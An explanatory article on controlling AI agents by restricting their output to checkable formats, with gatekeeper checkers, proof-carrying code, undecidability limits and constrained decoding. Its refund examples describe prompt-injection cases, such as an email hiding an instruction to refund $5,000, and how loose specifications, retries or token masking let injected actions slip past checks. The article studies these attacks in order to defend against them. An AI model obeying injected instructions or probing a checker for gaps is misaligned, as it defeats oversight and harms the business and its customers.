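# Restricting AI outputs to checkable languages and constrained formats

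## What it means to make an AI's output checkable

Restricting an AI to a checkable language is a way to control what it can do by limiting what it can write. The AI may produce only texts of a certain form, and a separate program tests each text before it has any effect. The form may be a list of permitted commands, a small language for plans, or a programming language without the features that are hardest to check. A narrower form usually lets the test establish more about each text, but it also limits what the AI can express.

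The AI is usually a language model, a program that continues text. It works on tokens, short pieces of text such as a word, part of a word or a comma. Given the tokens so far, the model computes a probability for each token that could come next. The surrounding software picks one, adds it to the text and runs the model again until the answer is complete. The result is only text, and it has effects when a person or another program acts on it.

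An agent is a language model that runs in a loop with other software. The model writes a request, and the software carries it out and adds the result to the text the model continues from. A tool call is a request that names a function and the values to pass to it. The loop also lets in text from strangers, which makes prompt injection possible, where someone plants instructions in an email, web page or file that the agent will read, and the model follows them as if its user had written them.

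### The gatekeeper

Suppose a shop's AI customer-service agent is allowed to refund customers up to 100 dollars. The agent proposes a refund by writing text in its output language, the set of texts that a grammar, a type system or a list allows it to produce. A checker, which is an ordinary program, then tests the text against a specification, a precise statement of what an output must or must not do. If the checker accepts the text, an interpreter, here the program that moves the money, carries it out. If the checker rejects it, no money moves, and the software either returns an error to the model, which can try again, or passes the case to an employee. This arrangement, in which an output takes effect only if the checker accepts it, is called a gatekeeper.

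The arrangement works only if the assistant has no other way to send money. If it also has the password to the payment system, it can bypass the checker. The specification must also define the limit precisely, because "up to 100 dollars" could mean per refund, per order, per customer or per day. A checker that looks at each refund alone will accept fifty refunds of 80 dollars to the same person. To enforce a limit per customer, it has to keep a running total for each one.

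### One refund, written four ways

Suppose a kettle arrived broken and the assistant decides to refund 80 dollars on order 4417. It could write to the payments desk in free text: "Please return 80 dollars to the customer on order 4417, and add something for the trouble." A checker can search this message for dollar amounts above 100 and find none, but "something for the trouble" has no fixed amount, so how much the customer gets depends on how the reader interprets it. A second language model could judge the message, but its judgment would also be a prediction, and an injected instruction that misled the first model may mislead the second too.

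A shell script, a series of commands to a computer's operating system, removes the vagueness:

```
price=$(lookup_price 4417)
refund --order 4417 --amount "$price"
```

A machine can carry out this script without guessing, but the script doesn't state an amount. The look-up may return 80 or 300, and nobody can tell which from the text. A script can also delete files, repeat a refund in a loop, or download another script and run it. The checker can confirm that the text is well-formed and search it for forbidden command names, but a script can assemble a name from fragments while it runs. No algorithm can predict the behaviour of every program in a language this powerful.

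As a typed tool call, in which each field has a declared kind of value, the same refund looks like this:

```
{"tool": "refund", "order": 4417, "amount_cents": 8000}
```

Now a few lines of code can confirm that the tool is on the permitted list, that the order number is a whole number and that the amount lies between 1 and 10,000 cents. If the checker can also read the shop's database, it can confirm that the order exists and that the customer paid at least 80 dollars for it. It cannot check whether the kettle was broken. The format also limits the assistant, which can no longer write "half the price" or "refund this once the warehouse has the parcel".

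A plan gives some of that back:

```
1. order = look_up(4417)
2. require order.paid_cents >= 8000
3. refund(order, 8000)
4. send_receipt(order)
```

Here the refund is the third step, and the checker sees the whole sequence before the first step runs. It can therefore check, for example, that no refund comes before the look-up, that the refunds total no more than 10,000 cents, and that the receipt goes to the address on the order rather than one that appeared in an email. But the assistant must choose its steps before it has seen any results. A plan language with branches and loops would relax this requirement and give the checker more to analyze.

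Suppose the customer's email contains a hidden instruction to refund 5,000 dollars. The model may well propose the refund, but the checker for tool calls will reject it. If the hidden instruction is instead to refund 80 dollars for a kettle that arrived intact, the checker will approve the proposal because it satisfies the specification. A gatekeeper limits the damage from a deceived model to whatever the specification permits, so a loose specification gives little protection.

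### Sound checks, complete checks

A checker can err by accepting an output that violates the specification or by rejecting one that satisfies it. Let S be the set of outputs that satisfy the specification and A the set that the checker accepts. The checker is sound if A is a subset of S, which rules out the first error, and complete if S is a subset of A, which rules out the second. Neither property is worth much alone, because a checker that rejects everything is sound and one that accepts everything is complete.

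For the range test on a tool call, A and S coincide. For richer languages, designers often have to give up one of the two properties, and where safety is the aim they give up completeness. For example, a checker for refund scripts might reject any script whose amount is not written out as a number. It would then reject the two-line script above even when the look-up would return 80. That error is safe, since no money moves, but each time the model has to try again, an employee has to step in, or the customer has to wait. If this happens often, the shop will be tempted to loosen the checker or switch it off. Rejection is also safe only where doing nothing is safe, so a controller for a vehicle's brakes needs an acceptable fallback action.

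Soundness matters more when checking an AI's output than a careful human's, because an AI can easily retry hundreds of times. Extra attempts can't get a bad output past a sound check, but if the check has a gap, they amount to a search for it, whether or not the model "intends" to find it.

### Why the language matters more than the model

The checker reads only the text that the AI produced and, where the specification calls for it, some records, not the AI itself. Its verdict on a refund of 8,000 cents is the same whether the text came from a reliable model, a hijacked one or an employee. The shop can therefore replace the model with a newer one and keep the checker. But if it lets the same model write shell scripts instead of tool calls, it needs a different checker, which may be impossible to build.

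Testing the model gives weaker assurance. *Safeguarded AI* (Dalrymple, 2024), the founding document of a British research programme, points out that an evaluation covers a finite set of prompts. It can prove that a problem exists, but finding none gives very little confidence about prompts that the testers did not try. Attacks by skilled testers have the same limit. The range test, by contrast, covers every amount that the assistant could write.

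The model's quality still matters, because the specification leaves open whether the customer deserves 80 dollars, 20 dollars or an apology. The shop depends on the model's judgement for that decision as much as before.

### Bytecode verification and proof-carrying code

Computer scientists worked on this problem for downloaded programs long before language models. In the 1990s, web browsers began to run Java applets, small compiled programs from sites that users had no reason to trust. Applets came as bytecode, instructions for a simulated computer called a virtual machine. In *Java bytecode verification*, Leroy called checking this bytecode a crucial security component for applets, both on the web and on smart cards.

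Before the program runs, the verifier goes through it and tracks the type of each value instead of the value itself. After an instruction that loads a number, it records "number". If a later instruction would use that number as the address of an object, the verifier rejects the program, because a program that can forge addresses can get around every other protection. Where two paths through the code meet, it keeps only the type information that holds on both. It also rejects programs that jump into the middle of system routines or into data. Some harmless programs are rejected too, such as one with a type error in a branch that never executes.

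Microsoft's .NET platform later adopted a similar check for its own intermediate code, though it let fully trusted programs skip it. The quality of such a check depends on how precisely it is specified. *Improving the official specification of Java bytecode verification* (Coglio, 2003) warned that inadequacies in Java's official specification could lead to unsound verifiers, which let attackers break security, or incomplete ones, which reject legal programs.

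Bytecode verification establishes a fixed set of properties for programs in one language. Proof-carrying code, which George Necula and Peter Lee developed at Carnegie Mellon University, lets whoever runs the program choose the properties, and leaves the hard work of proving them to whoever supplies it. *Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking* (Necula and Lee, 1996) considers an operating system's kernel, its most privileged part, which has to run machine code from an untrusted user. The kernel publishes a safety policy, and the user sends the code and a formal proof that it obeys the policy. The kernel checks the proof and, if it is valid, runs the code at full speed with no further checks.

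One of their examples is a table in the kernel's memory. Each entry has a tag and, eight bytes further on, a data word. The kernel calls the user's code with the address of that user's entry in a register, r0. The code may always read both words, but may write the data word only if the tag is not zero. In the notation of the policy, rd(a) means that address a is safe to read, wr(a) that it is safe to write, and mem(a) stands for the contents of a. The kernel then promises, as a precondition:

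```
rd(r0)  and  rd(r0+8)  and  (if mem(r0) ≠ 0 then wr(r0+8))
```

Suppose the user's program has four instructions: read the tag into r1; if r1 is zero, skip the next instruction; write to r0+8; return. A procedure called a verification-condition generator works backwards from the end. The return adds no requirement. The write requires wr(r0+8). The conditional skip weakens this to "if r1 ≠ 0 then wr(r0+8)". The read adds rd(r0) and replaces r1 with what it loaded:

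```
rd(r0)  and  (if mem(r0) ≠ 0 then wr(r0+8))
```

Both parts are in the precondition, so the proof is short. If the programmer leaves out the conditional skip, the requirement becomes "rd(r0) and wr(r0+8)". The precondition doesn't grant the write unconditionally, so no valid proof exists and the kernel rejects the program.

The user cannot cheat by proving an easier statement, because the kernel computes for itself what must be proved. Necula observed in *Proof-Carrying Code* that tampering with the code or the proof usually makes validation fail, and that in the few cases where validation still succeeds, the changed code is safe too. The kernel's owner has to trust the small program that checks proofs and the soundness of the policy, but not the supplier.

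Necula and Lee tried this on network packet filters, programs that decide which incoding data to pass on. Each proof took 1 to 3 milliseconds to check and had to be checked only once. The filters then ran faster than versions made safe by the competing methods of the time. Producing the proofs was harder. Necula and Lee automated this for the filters, which contained no loops, but did not expect a fully automatic method for programs in general. For code with loops, someone must also find an invariant for each loop, a statement that stays true on every pass.

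### From guaranteed safe AI to ARIA's programme

Capable AI systems can take over much of that search, and a gatekeeper can use what they find without trusting them. In 2024 David Dalrymple and other researchers generalised the scheme under the name "guaranteed safe AI". It has three parts: a world model, which describes mathematically how the AI's outputs affect the world; a safety specification, which describes the acceptable effects; and a verifier, which produces a proof that anyone can audit. An overview page, *Guaranteed-Safe AI*, describes a gatekeeper that stands between users and a potentially dangerous system and lets only provably safe actions through. According to the overview, the approach depends on having the right concepts to describe the world, but not on finding out what the AI privately knows.

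That dependence is the big step beyond Necula and Lee's work. A checker can test "the amount is at most 10,000 cents" from the text alone, but it needs a model of how customers behave to test "false claims will cost the shop less than 1 per cent of its sales". Dalrymple accepted that, for AI in general, a specification that mentions only a system's inputs and outputs can capture some useful properties but no physical kind of safety. His gatekeeper was therefore more than a checker, with AI systems that would help experts build the world model, search for proofs that the probability of harm stays below a stated bound, and train controllers that are easy to verify. People still dispute how much of the world can be formalised this way.

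Dalrymple wrote this as a programme director at ARIA, the UK's Advanced Research and Invention Agency. The programme aimed to show that such a gatekeeper could run something like an electricity grid or a supply chain. He hoped success would persuade governments to use the most powerful AI only inside systems with quantitative guarantees. He estimated that it would be rational for them to agree if the research took less than 15 years and yielded more than 5 per cent of the value of unconstrained AI along the way.

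ARIA has since cancelled the machine-learning part of the programme, worth £18m, in November 2025, shortly before applications closed. In an ARIA interview that month, *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025), Dalrymple explained that general-purpose models had improved faster than expected and would probably acquire the needed skills without a dedicated team. ARIA also dropped a planned second call for projects in physical settings such as energy, and Dalrymple moved to an advisory role. In the rewritten thesis *Safeguarded AI* (May 2026), his successor, Ammann, judged timely international consensus on a gatekeeper workflow less likely than before and turned the programme towards making society more resilient.

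These reasons concern the speed of AI progress and the prospects for agreement, and none is a finding that gatekeepers fail. But the demonstration meant to settle whether a gatekeeper can handle a complicated physical system is now further off. Ammann's design still uses the division of labour from proof-carrying code, with AI doing the searching and a checker that "stays small and trusted". Ammann expects trust to depend more on the specifications and the assumptions around them, which people will have to audit.

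ARIA's *Safeguarded AI* programme runs until the end of 2027. Its programme page lists £59m in total backing, including £22m for eight cybersecurity projects with aims that range from containing AI agents to protecting code on millions of Android devices. The programme's funding page has a rolling call for more teams to build security-critical software with machine-checked proofs of its key properties. These teams will work in eight-week cycles, and a separate team will attack each verified system.

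## Which properties can be decided in which languages

The range test on a refund call always finishes and gives the right answer. The property it checks is decidable, meaning that some algorithm gives the correct answer in finite time for every input. No algorithm can decide, for every shell script, whether it will ever refund more than 100 dollars. The proof starts from the simpler question of whether a given program ever stops.

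### The halting problem

Suppose someone has written a function halts(p, x) that takes the text of any program p and any input x. It always returns the right answer: yes if p eventually stops on x, no if p runs forever. Hamkins and Nenu (2024), in *Did Turing prove the undecidability of the halting problem?*, give the usual argument against such a function, which uses it to build a short program q:

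```
q(p):
    if halts(p, p):  loop forever
    else:            stop
```

The program q takes the text of a program p, calls halts to check whether p stops when given its own text, and then does the opposite. A program can take its own text as input, just as a spelling checker can check the file that contains its own source code. When q is given its own text, it loops forever if halts(q, q) returns yes and stops if it returns no. Either answer is wrong, so no function can do what halts was supposed to do.

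The argument applies to any language whose programs can read text, call functions, branch and loop. It doesn't depend on how `halts` works, so it rules out a neural network in that role as well as a hand-written analyzer.

Textbooks usually credit the proof that the halting problem is undecidable to Alan Turing's 1936 paper on computable numbers, but Hamkins and Nenu point out that the paper never discusses halting. Turing designed his machines to run forever, and he proved that no algorithm can tell whether a machine will ever print a given symbol. That question translates easily into the halting problem. Stephen Kleene published the familiar argument in 1952, and Martin Davis introduced the name "halting problem" in 1958. Turing evidently had his own proof, since Strachey recalled in *An impossible program* (1965) that he had heard one from Turing in 1953.

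### From halting to division by zero

Most specifications concern properties other than halting. *Coding Guidelines and Undecidability* (Bagnara, Bagnara and Hill, 2022) shows how these properties can be undecidable too, using division by zero as an example. If every division in a C program p goes through a guard that returns 0 when the divisor is 0, then p never divides by zero. The guard doesn't limit what C can compute, so whether such programs halt is still undecidable. Inserting a deliberate division by zero just before each point where p ends produces a program that divides by zero exactly when p halts. A tool that could decide whether any given C program divides by zero would therefore solve the halting problem, so no such tool can exist.

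The same trick works for almost any event. If we insert a 5,000-dollar refund where a script with no other refunds ends, the new script breaks the shop's limit exactly when the original would finish. No checker can tell for every such script whether it will finish, so none can tell for every script whether it will break the limit.

Running a program can confirm that it halts on a given input, but not that it runs forever, because it might always stop at the next step. Specifications that forbid an event are hard to confirm for the same reason. A test run can reveal a division by zero but can't prove that one will never happen. A specification usually also has to hold for every input. Bagnara and colleagues note that whether a program halts on all inputs would remain undecidable even with an oracle that could decide whether it halts on any single input.

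### Rice's theorem

Rice (1953), in *Classes of Recursively Enumerable Sets and Their Decision Problems*, proved a limit that applies to any property of what programs compute, as opposed to how they are written. If some programs have the property and others lack it, no algorithm can decide for every program whether that program has it.

A checker can easily test properties of a program's text, such as how many if-statements it has or whether it contains loops. Restricted languages rely on such tests because a condition on the text can guarantee something about the program's behaviour. For instance, a program without loops or recursive calls always stops, provided that each of its instructions does.

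Rice's theorem rules out a single method that works for all programs. It does not put any particular program beyond proof, though people sometimes cite it as if it did. Rice himself added that "special methods for particular functions" will exist. For example, a program that prints "hello" and stops plainly halts. A yes-or-no question about one fixed program is always decidable in the technical sense, because either the algorithm that prints "yes" or the one that prints "no" is correct, even if nobody knows which.

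A gatekeeper only needs to recognise enough good programs to get the work done, not judge every possible program. An AI trying to get its program accepted can write one that is easy to check.

### A ladder of languages

How much a checker can settle depends on the language. The table runs roughly from the weakest languages to the strongest.

| Language | What it can express | What a checker can always decide | Cost |
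|---|---|---|---|
| Finite list | A fixed menu of actions | Anything that someone can establish about each entry | One examination per entry |
| Finite automaton | Order and repetition, with a fixed memory | Whether a text fits; whether two automata accept the same texts | About n log n steps to compare two automata with n states |
| Context-free grammar | Nesting to any depth | Whether a text fits; whether any text does | At most the cube of the text's length, to test one text |
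| Bounded loops over fixed-size data | Calculations of limited size | In principle, every question about results | Up to 2^n combinations of values for n bits |
| Total language with unbounded integers | Nearly every function that people use | That every program stops | A run can outlast the galaxy |
| Turing-complete language | Every computation | Nothing about results that varies between programs | No limit |

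A list of permitted actions is only as safe as the actions on it. If one of three permitted actions is "run the script in this file", checking the output is as hard as checking arbitrary programs in the scripting language.

A finite automaton reads a sequence and moves between a fixed number of states. To enforce "no refund before a look-up", it can start in a state that doesn't allow refunds and move to one that does after a look-up. Because there are few states, a program can visit them all to check whether the automaton can ever reach a bad one, a technique called model checking. A program can also compare two automata, so a shop that revises its rules can find out whether the old and new versions permit exactly the same sequences. Veldhuizen's *Tradeoffs in Metaprogramming* gives the amount of computation this comparison requires.

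An automaton can't count without limit. According to the textbook slides *Formal Language, chapter 18*, it can't recognize the texts that consist of some number of a's followed by the same number of b's, but a context-free grammar can describe them. The rules of such a grammar can refer to themselves, so an expression may be a pair of brackets around another expression. Most data formats and programming languages rely on this kind of nesting. Checking whether a text fits a grammar is still practical, but no algorithm can tell for every pair of context-free grammars whether they produce the same texts.

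The reason is again the halting problem. A grammar can describe all the texts that are not a correct and complete record of a program's run, because one mistake is enough to make a record invalid and a grammar can describe each kind of mistake. If the program never halts, no complete record exists, so the grammar produces every possible text. Comparing it with a grammar for "any text at all" would therefore show whether the program halts. So a team that rewrites the grammar of its output language may have no tool that can confirm the new version permits the same texts, even though the checker can still test each text.

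A program with a fixed amount of data is a finite automaton in compact form. Ten 32-bit variables can hold about 10^96 combinations of values, and a checker could in principle go through them all. If the loops also have fixed limits, the checker can unroll them, copying each loop's body as many times as the loop may run, and give the result to a solver as one long logical formula. This often works well, but nobody knows a method that is fast on every formula.

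Real computers have finite memory as well, so strictly speaking the halting problem for a laptop is decidable. This helps little in practice because eight gigabytes of memory have 2 to the power of 64 billion possible states.

### What guaranteed termination leaves open

Total languages keep unbounded numbers but let no program run forever. Meyer and Ritchie, in *The complexity of loop programs*, studied a tiny one in 1967. A Loop program can copy a register, add 1 to it, set it to 0 or repeat a block of instructions, as here:

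```
LOOP X
    X = X + 1
END
```

This program doubles X and stops, because LOOP fixes the number of repetitions before the first one begins. Such programs can add, multiply, raise to powers and find the x-th prime number. Meyer and Ritchie wrote that it takes a fairly careful analysis to find a computable function that these programs cannot compute.

The depth of loop nesting gives an upper bound on a program's running time. For loops nested one deep, the bound comes from applying the function 2x repeatedly, once for each instruction. For two levels the function is 2^x, and for three it is a tower of x twos, each the exponent of the one below. Meyer and Ritchie remarked that a seven-level program that needs all the time allowed "might just as well contain an infinite loop", because on inputs larger than two it would not finish within the lifetime of the Milky Way.

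Even apart from speed, knowing that a program stops doesn't reveal what it does first. Take any program p, in any language, with a fixed input, and write this one:

```
t(n):
    run p for n steps
    if p has stopped by then:  return 0
    else:                      return 1
```

Given a program p, let t be the program that takes a number n, runs p for n steps, and returns 0 if p has halted by then and 1 otherwise. A total language can express t, since the number of steps is known at the start and t always finishes. But t returns 0 for some n exactly when p halts, so an algorithm that could tell whether a total program ever outputs 0 would solve the halting problem. Rice noted that his theorem carries over to the primitive recursive functions, which are exactly the functions that Loop programs compute.

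Running time has the same problem. In a program that sets T to 0 and then repeats a huge block T times, the block never runs, so the depth of loop nesting greatly overstates the time needed. A programmer can add a rule to the checker that detects this case, but Meyer and Ritchie proved that no algorithm can detect all such cases once loops are nested three deep.

The question about all inputs remains undecidable. For one known n, the checker can run t(n) and look at the result. If a refund script in a total language depends only on data the checker already has, a trial run on a copy of the shop's records shows what the script will do, as long as the run is short enough and the records don't change before the real run.

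The Loop language becomes Turing-complete with one small addition, a loop that repeats until some condition holds, with no limit fixed in advance. Designers of simple formats have sometimes made them Turing-complete by accident.

### The price in program length

Programs can be much longer in a total language, where every program halts, than in a general-purpose language. Manuel Blum quantified this in *On the size of machines* (1967), and Robert Harper's blog post *Old Neglected Theorems Are Still Theorems* (2014) explains the result. For any total language L and any factor, however large, L can express some function whose shortest program in L is at least that many times as long as its shortest program in a general-purpose language.

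To see why, let n be a large number and F(n) a much larger length computed from it, such as 2^(2^n). We can write a program in a general-purpose language that lists every program in L of up to F(n) characters. On input i, it runs the i-th program in the list with i as its input and returns the result plus 1. If the list has no i-th program, it returns 0.

This program always finishes, because every program in L does. Its results differ from those of each listed program on at least one input, so no program in L of F(n) characters or fewer computes the same function. L can still express the function with a long enough table of values, because the function is 0 on all but finitely many inputs. The general-purpose program needs only an interpreter for L, a formula for F and the digits of n, which together fit into fewer than n characters once n is large enough.

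The function is contrived, and Harper concedes that the theorem guarantees only that a bad case exists. But he also gives a natural example, the greatest common divisor of two numbers, here with the case of equal numbers included:

```
gcd(m, 0) = m
gcd(0, n) = n
gcd(m, n) = gcd(m - n, n)    if m >= n
gcd(m, n) = gcd(m, n - m)    if m < n
```

In Gödel's T, a total language, recursion can only count down by one at a time. A programmer can still write gcd in it, but the code is awkward and needs a hidden counter that slows it down. A more permissive total language would handle gcd easily but have trouble with other programs. Harper attributes these problems to the proof of termination, which a total language requires the code itself to contain. *Auto formalisation of Chaitin and of the surprise incompleteness Theorem* (2026) makes the same connection: there is no limit to how much shorter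 a program can be if the proof that it stops may be kept outside it.

Weaker languages also have a drawback, which is that they can require much longer programs. Veldhuizen points out that some C programs recognise patterns that a finite automaton could also recognise, but writing those patterns as regular expressions, the usual notation for them, would take 10^100 times as many characters. This doesn't matter for a four-line refund plan, but it starts to matter when the AI has to write an algorithm.

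Some functions cannot be written in a total language at all. The standard example is the language's own interpreter, a function run(p, x) that returns whatever program p returns on x. If the language contained run, it would also contain d(p) = run(p, p) + 1, and d applied to its own text would have to return one more than the value it returns. According to a discussion on the blog Mathematics and Computation (2016), such claims rest on assumptions that people seldom state, so the result depends heavily on what counts as an interpreter.

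### Decidable but impractical

A decidable question may also take too long to answer. Presburger arithmetic consists of statements about whole numbers that use addition, comparison, the logical words "and", "or" and "not", and the quantifiers "for all" and "there is". It doesn't allow one variable to be multiplied by another. It can express, for example, that 3-cent and 5-cent coins can make up every amount from 8 cents upwards:

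```
for all x:  if x >= 8, there are a and b such that
            x = a + a + a + b + b + b + b + b
```

In 1929 Mojżesz Presburger gave an algorithm that decides every first-order statement about whole numbers that uses only addition and comparison. It removes the quantifiers from the inside outwards, so that "there is a y such that x = y + y" becomes "x is even", until only sums and comparisons of plain numbers remain. If the language also allows multiplication of variables, no algorithm can decide every statement.

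In 1974 Michael Fischer and Michael Rabin proved that any algorithm for Presburger arithmetic needs at least 2^(2^(cn)) steps on some statements of length n, where c is a positive constant. If c were 0.1, some statements of 100 symbols would take at least 2^1024 steps, a number with 309 digits.

The statements that are hardest to decide switch many times between "for all" and "there is". Program checkers tend to produce statements with few of these quantifiers or none, and solvers often settle them in a fraction of a second. Decidability doesn't guarantee an answer in the time a customer will wait, so a designer has to test the checker on realistic outputs.

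### Three ways to check a rich language anyway

If the shop does need its assistant to write programs in a rich language, the checker can reject any program it can't decide either way. Bagnara and colleagues say a good tool for an undecidable rule gives one of three answers: yes, no or don't know. Many tools answer only yes or no. In doubtful cases, some of these report nothing, which makes them unsuitable for safety work. Others report a violation, which is sound but becomes a nuisance if it happens too often.

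Suppose a checker tracks only the range of each variable. If x lies between 0 and 10, it computes that x - x lies between -10 and 10, and x - x + 1 between -9 and 11. That range includes 0, so the checker rejects a division by x - x + 1, although the value is always 1. The program's author can simplify the expression and try again. Alternatively, the undecidable rule against dividing by zero can be replaced with a stricter one about the program's text, such as "divide only through the guard function". People who write coding standards face this choice. MISRA C, a rulebook for critical software, marks 37 of its 158 rules as undecidable.

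The gatekeeper can instead require the author to supply what the checker cannot find, as Necula and Lee's kernel did. For gcd, the one-line annotation "m + n gets smaller with each call" is enough. The checker must then confirm that (m - n) + n is less than m + n when n is above 0, and that m + (n - m) is less than m + n when m is above 0. Both are easy statements of Presburger arithmetic. Since m + n can never fall below 0, the calls must end. Harper describes the NuPRL system, which keeps the proof beside the program in this way so that the proof doesn't slow the program down.

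Checking a complete formal proof is decidable, because a program can check each step against the rules. Finding a proof may take decades, as Harper illustrates with the Collatz conjecture, which concerns whether a very simple loop always stops. A restricted language doesn't avoid this work. Veldhuizen proved, for programs that generate other programs, that rewriting one in a language that guarantees a property amounts to proving that it has the property. Either way, whoever writes the program has to do the proving, and if that is an AI, the organization using it has to supply the computing time.

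A third approach is to run the program and cut it off at a fixed limit, such as a million steps. Every program then stops, so the halting problem no longer arises. The Ethereum blockchain does this with programs from strangers. Each instruction uses up "gas" that someone has paid for, and if the gas runs out, the system stops the program and undoes its changes. Total languages also need a cap, because a Loop program can run for a very long time.

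A cap on steps does not control what a program does before reaching the cap. To control that, the interpreter has to check each action when the program requests it. By then the refund is a plain number, so the interpreter can check its range as it would for a tool call. But the shop no longer knows before the program starts whether the whole program follows the rules. If the script breaks a rule at its third refund, the first two have already gone out, unless the interpreter holds every payment and email until the run ends. It can't do that if the script needs a customer's reply before it can continue.

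## Making a language model write only valid output

Constrained decoding can keep a model from writing malformed text. At each step of generation, software blocks the tokens that cannot lead to valid output. A checker that reads finished text, by contrast, can only accept or reject it.

### Masking one token at a time

The software has to judge unfinished text, which an ordinary parser can't do. A parser for the shop's tool calls would reject `{"tool": "ref` because the call is incomplete, although a few more characters would complete it. Mündler, He and colleagues (2025), in *Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models*, define the test that constrained decoding needs instead. An unfinished text s passes if some continuation turns it into a text in the output language L. All the texts that pass form the prefix language of L:

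```
prefix(L) = { s : some continuation s' makes s + s' a text in L }
```

An incremental parser reads the text piece by piece and keeps track of what may come next, so it can apply this test at every token. Each step of generation then works like this:

1. The model computes a probability for every token in its vocabulary.
2. The parser finds the tokens that would keep the text in prefix(L).
3. The software masks all the others, which means setting their probability to zero, and divides the remaining probabilities by their sum so that they add up to 1 again.
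4. It draws one token according to these probabilities, adds it to the text and advances the parser.

Suppose the grammar for refund calls allows amounts from 1 to 10,000 cents, each digit is one token, and the text so far ends in `"amount_cents": 800`. The model assigns a probability of 70 per cent to another 0, 20 per cent to a comma and 10 per cent to the closing bracket. No field may follow the amount, so the software masks the comma, which raises the probabilities of the 0 and the bracket to 87.5 and 12.5 per cent. If the software draws the 0, the amount becomes 8000. Any further digit would exceed the limit, so the grammar then allows only the closing bracket.

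The same mechanism can produce a refund that nobody asked for. If an injected instruction leads the model to write 500000 cents, the mask lets 5000 through, blocks the next zero and forces the closing bracket. The shop then pays out 50 dollars, whereas a checker reading unconstrained text would have rejected the whole call. *Parsed, Plausible, Wrong* (2026), a study of small models that turn café orders into structured data, distinguishes detectable errors from silent ones. When an error is detectable, the output does not parse and the caller can ask again. When it is silent, the output parses but is wrong. A mask can turn detectable errors into silent ones. The shop can reduce this risk by using the mask to enforce only the form of the call and leaving the amount to the checker.

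Masked text still needs the checker. *Attention Meets Reachability* (2026) proves that masked text is in the output language if generation finishes, but generation may hit a length limit first and leave an incomplete call.

### Schemas, grammars and tokens

The output language is most often JSON, as in the refund call. A schema lists the permitted fields and the type of each value, and the software translates it into rules that an incremental parser can follow. Other formats need a grammar or, for simple patterns, a regular expression. In an example from Microsoft's *AI Controller Interface*, an early system for controlling generation, a model is asked to multiply 122.3 by 140.4, and a regular expression restricts its output to a number. The model can still give a number other than the correct answer, 17,170.92.

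*Flexible and Efficient Grammar-Constrained Decoding* (2025) attributes most of the engineering difficulty to a mismatch between the model's tokens and the grammar's symbols. A grammar treats a word such as `bvand`, an operator on strings of bits, as one symbol, but the model may write it as several tokens. A token may also contain the end of one symbol and the start of the next. *The Parser Already Knows* (Özgü, Wu and colleagues, 2026) describes the usual solution, which is to add a lexer alongside the parser. After the model has written `bv`, the lexer records that `bvand`, `bvlshr` and `bvor` are still possible, and the parser moves on only when one of them is complete. Microsoft's system also stores the vocabulary as a tree in which tokens that start the same way share a branch, so one forbidden character can rule out many tokens.

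Constrained decoding requires control over the model's next-token probabilities. *Prove What You Can* (2026) notes that companies that host models generally don't give customers this control, though several enforce JSON schemas on their own servers. A customer with a custom output language may therefore have to encode it as JSON, run an open model, or check the text after it is generated.

### Constraining types as well as syntax

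Code can be grammatical and still fail to compile. When Mündler and colleagues had six open models write TypeScript, a version of JavaScript with declared types, only 6 per cent of the compilation errors were syntax errors. The other 94 per cent came from breaking the type rules, which a context-free grammar generally can't express.

In an example from Mündler and colleagues, a model has written `parseInt(num`, where `num` is a number but `parseInt` expects a string. CodeLlama 34B continued with `, 10)`, which is valid syntax but causes a type error. To prevent this, the researchers built an automaton that tracks the declared variables and the type required at each point. Their software then searches for operations that lead from the current type to the required one. Here it blocks the comma because `num` is still a number, and allows the full stop that begins `.toString()` because calling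 that function returns a string.

Running this search for every token in the vocabulary was so slow that every test problem timed out after five minutes. The final version draws a token, checks it, and draws again only if the token fails. With the smallest model, the first draw passed 99.4 per cent of the time. Generation still took 39 per cent longer on HumanEval and 52 per cent longer on MBPP, two standard sets of short programming problems.

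Type constraints cut compilation errors by 75 per cent on HumanEval and 56 per cent on MBPP when the models wrote programs from scratch. Perfect enforcement of syntax alone would have cut them by 9 and 5 per cent. The share of programs that passed their tests rose by only 3.5 per cent in relative terms, because a program that compiles can still produce the wrong result.

The constraining software covered only part of TypeScript, however, so Mündler and colleagues first let each model write freely. They applied the constraints to a second attempt only when the first did not compile, so that they could not lose a program that already worked.

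### How masking distorts the model's choices

Masking also changes which valid outputs a model tends to write. Suppose the first token is A with probability 90 per cent and B with probability 10 per cent. Of the texts the model would write after A, 1 per cent are valid, while everything it would write after B is valid. Without constraints, it produces a valid text that starts with A 0.9 per cent of the time and one that starts with B 10 per cent of the time. Among its own valid outputs, A's share is therefore

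```
0.009 / (0.009 + 0.1) = 8.3 per cent
```

With masking, the model still starts with A 90 per cent of the time, because the mask allows any start that at least one valid text shares. The mask takes effect only later, when it forces the model into continuations to which the model assigns very low probability.

An exact correction would multiply each token's probability by the chance that the model, writing freely from there, would end with a valid text. A would get 0.9 × 0.01 and B would get 0.1 × 1, which restores the right shares. But computing that chance means adding up all possible continuations, which is impractical, so researchers approximate it:

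- **Repeated sampling.** A method called ASAp, which Park and colleagues published in 2024, draws many texts and adjusts the probabilities according to which beginnings turned out badly. Others use Monte Carlo methods to keep several drafts going or to revise a finished one. All this takes extra computing time for every request.
- **A learned correction.** SHIM, by Özgü and colleagues, trains a small model on 1,000 free outputs per grammar to predict from the state of the parser and lexer whether a text will end up valid. Its distribution was four to five times closer to the right one than masking's, by a standard measure of divergence, and it ran at most 25 per cent slower. ASAp ran up to 20 times slower than masking.
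- **Training the model itself.** Tuccio, Furnari and colleagues (2026), in *GrammarRL*, reward a model for valid outputs that its original version finds likely and from which that version can reconstruct the input. Scores on three tasks rose by 9.8 points on average over plain masking, with no extra work when the model is in use.

### Masking compared with retrying

Letting the model write freely and discarding whatever the checker rejects avoids the distortion. In the example, 10.9 per cent of attempts are valid, so the shop needs about nine attempts on average for each valid text. Of the accepted texts, 8.3 per cent start with A.

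At first sight, a proof by Nguyen, Silva and colleagues (2026), in *Constrained Decoding*, seems to contradict the charge of distortion. They show that masking never makes a valid answer less likely. Let P(y) be the probability that the model writes the valid text y freely, and let Z₁ to Zₙ be the total probability of the permitted tokens at each of its n steps. Then

```
P_masked(y) = P(y) / (Z₁ × Z₂ × ... × Zₙ)
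```

No Z is greater than 1, so masking produces y with probability at least P(y), its probability in a single free attempt. In the example, masking leaves texts that start with B at 10 per cent and raises valid texts that start with A from 0.9 to 90 per cent. If the shop instead retries until the checker accepts a text, 91.7 per cent of the results start with B. So if the right answer starts with B, masking does no worse than one free attempt but far worse than retrying.

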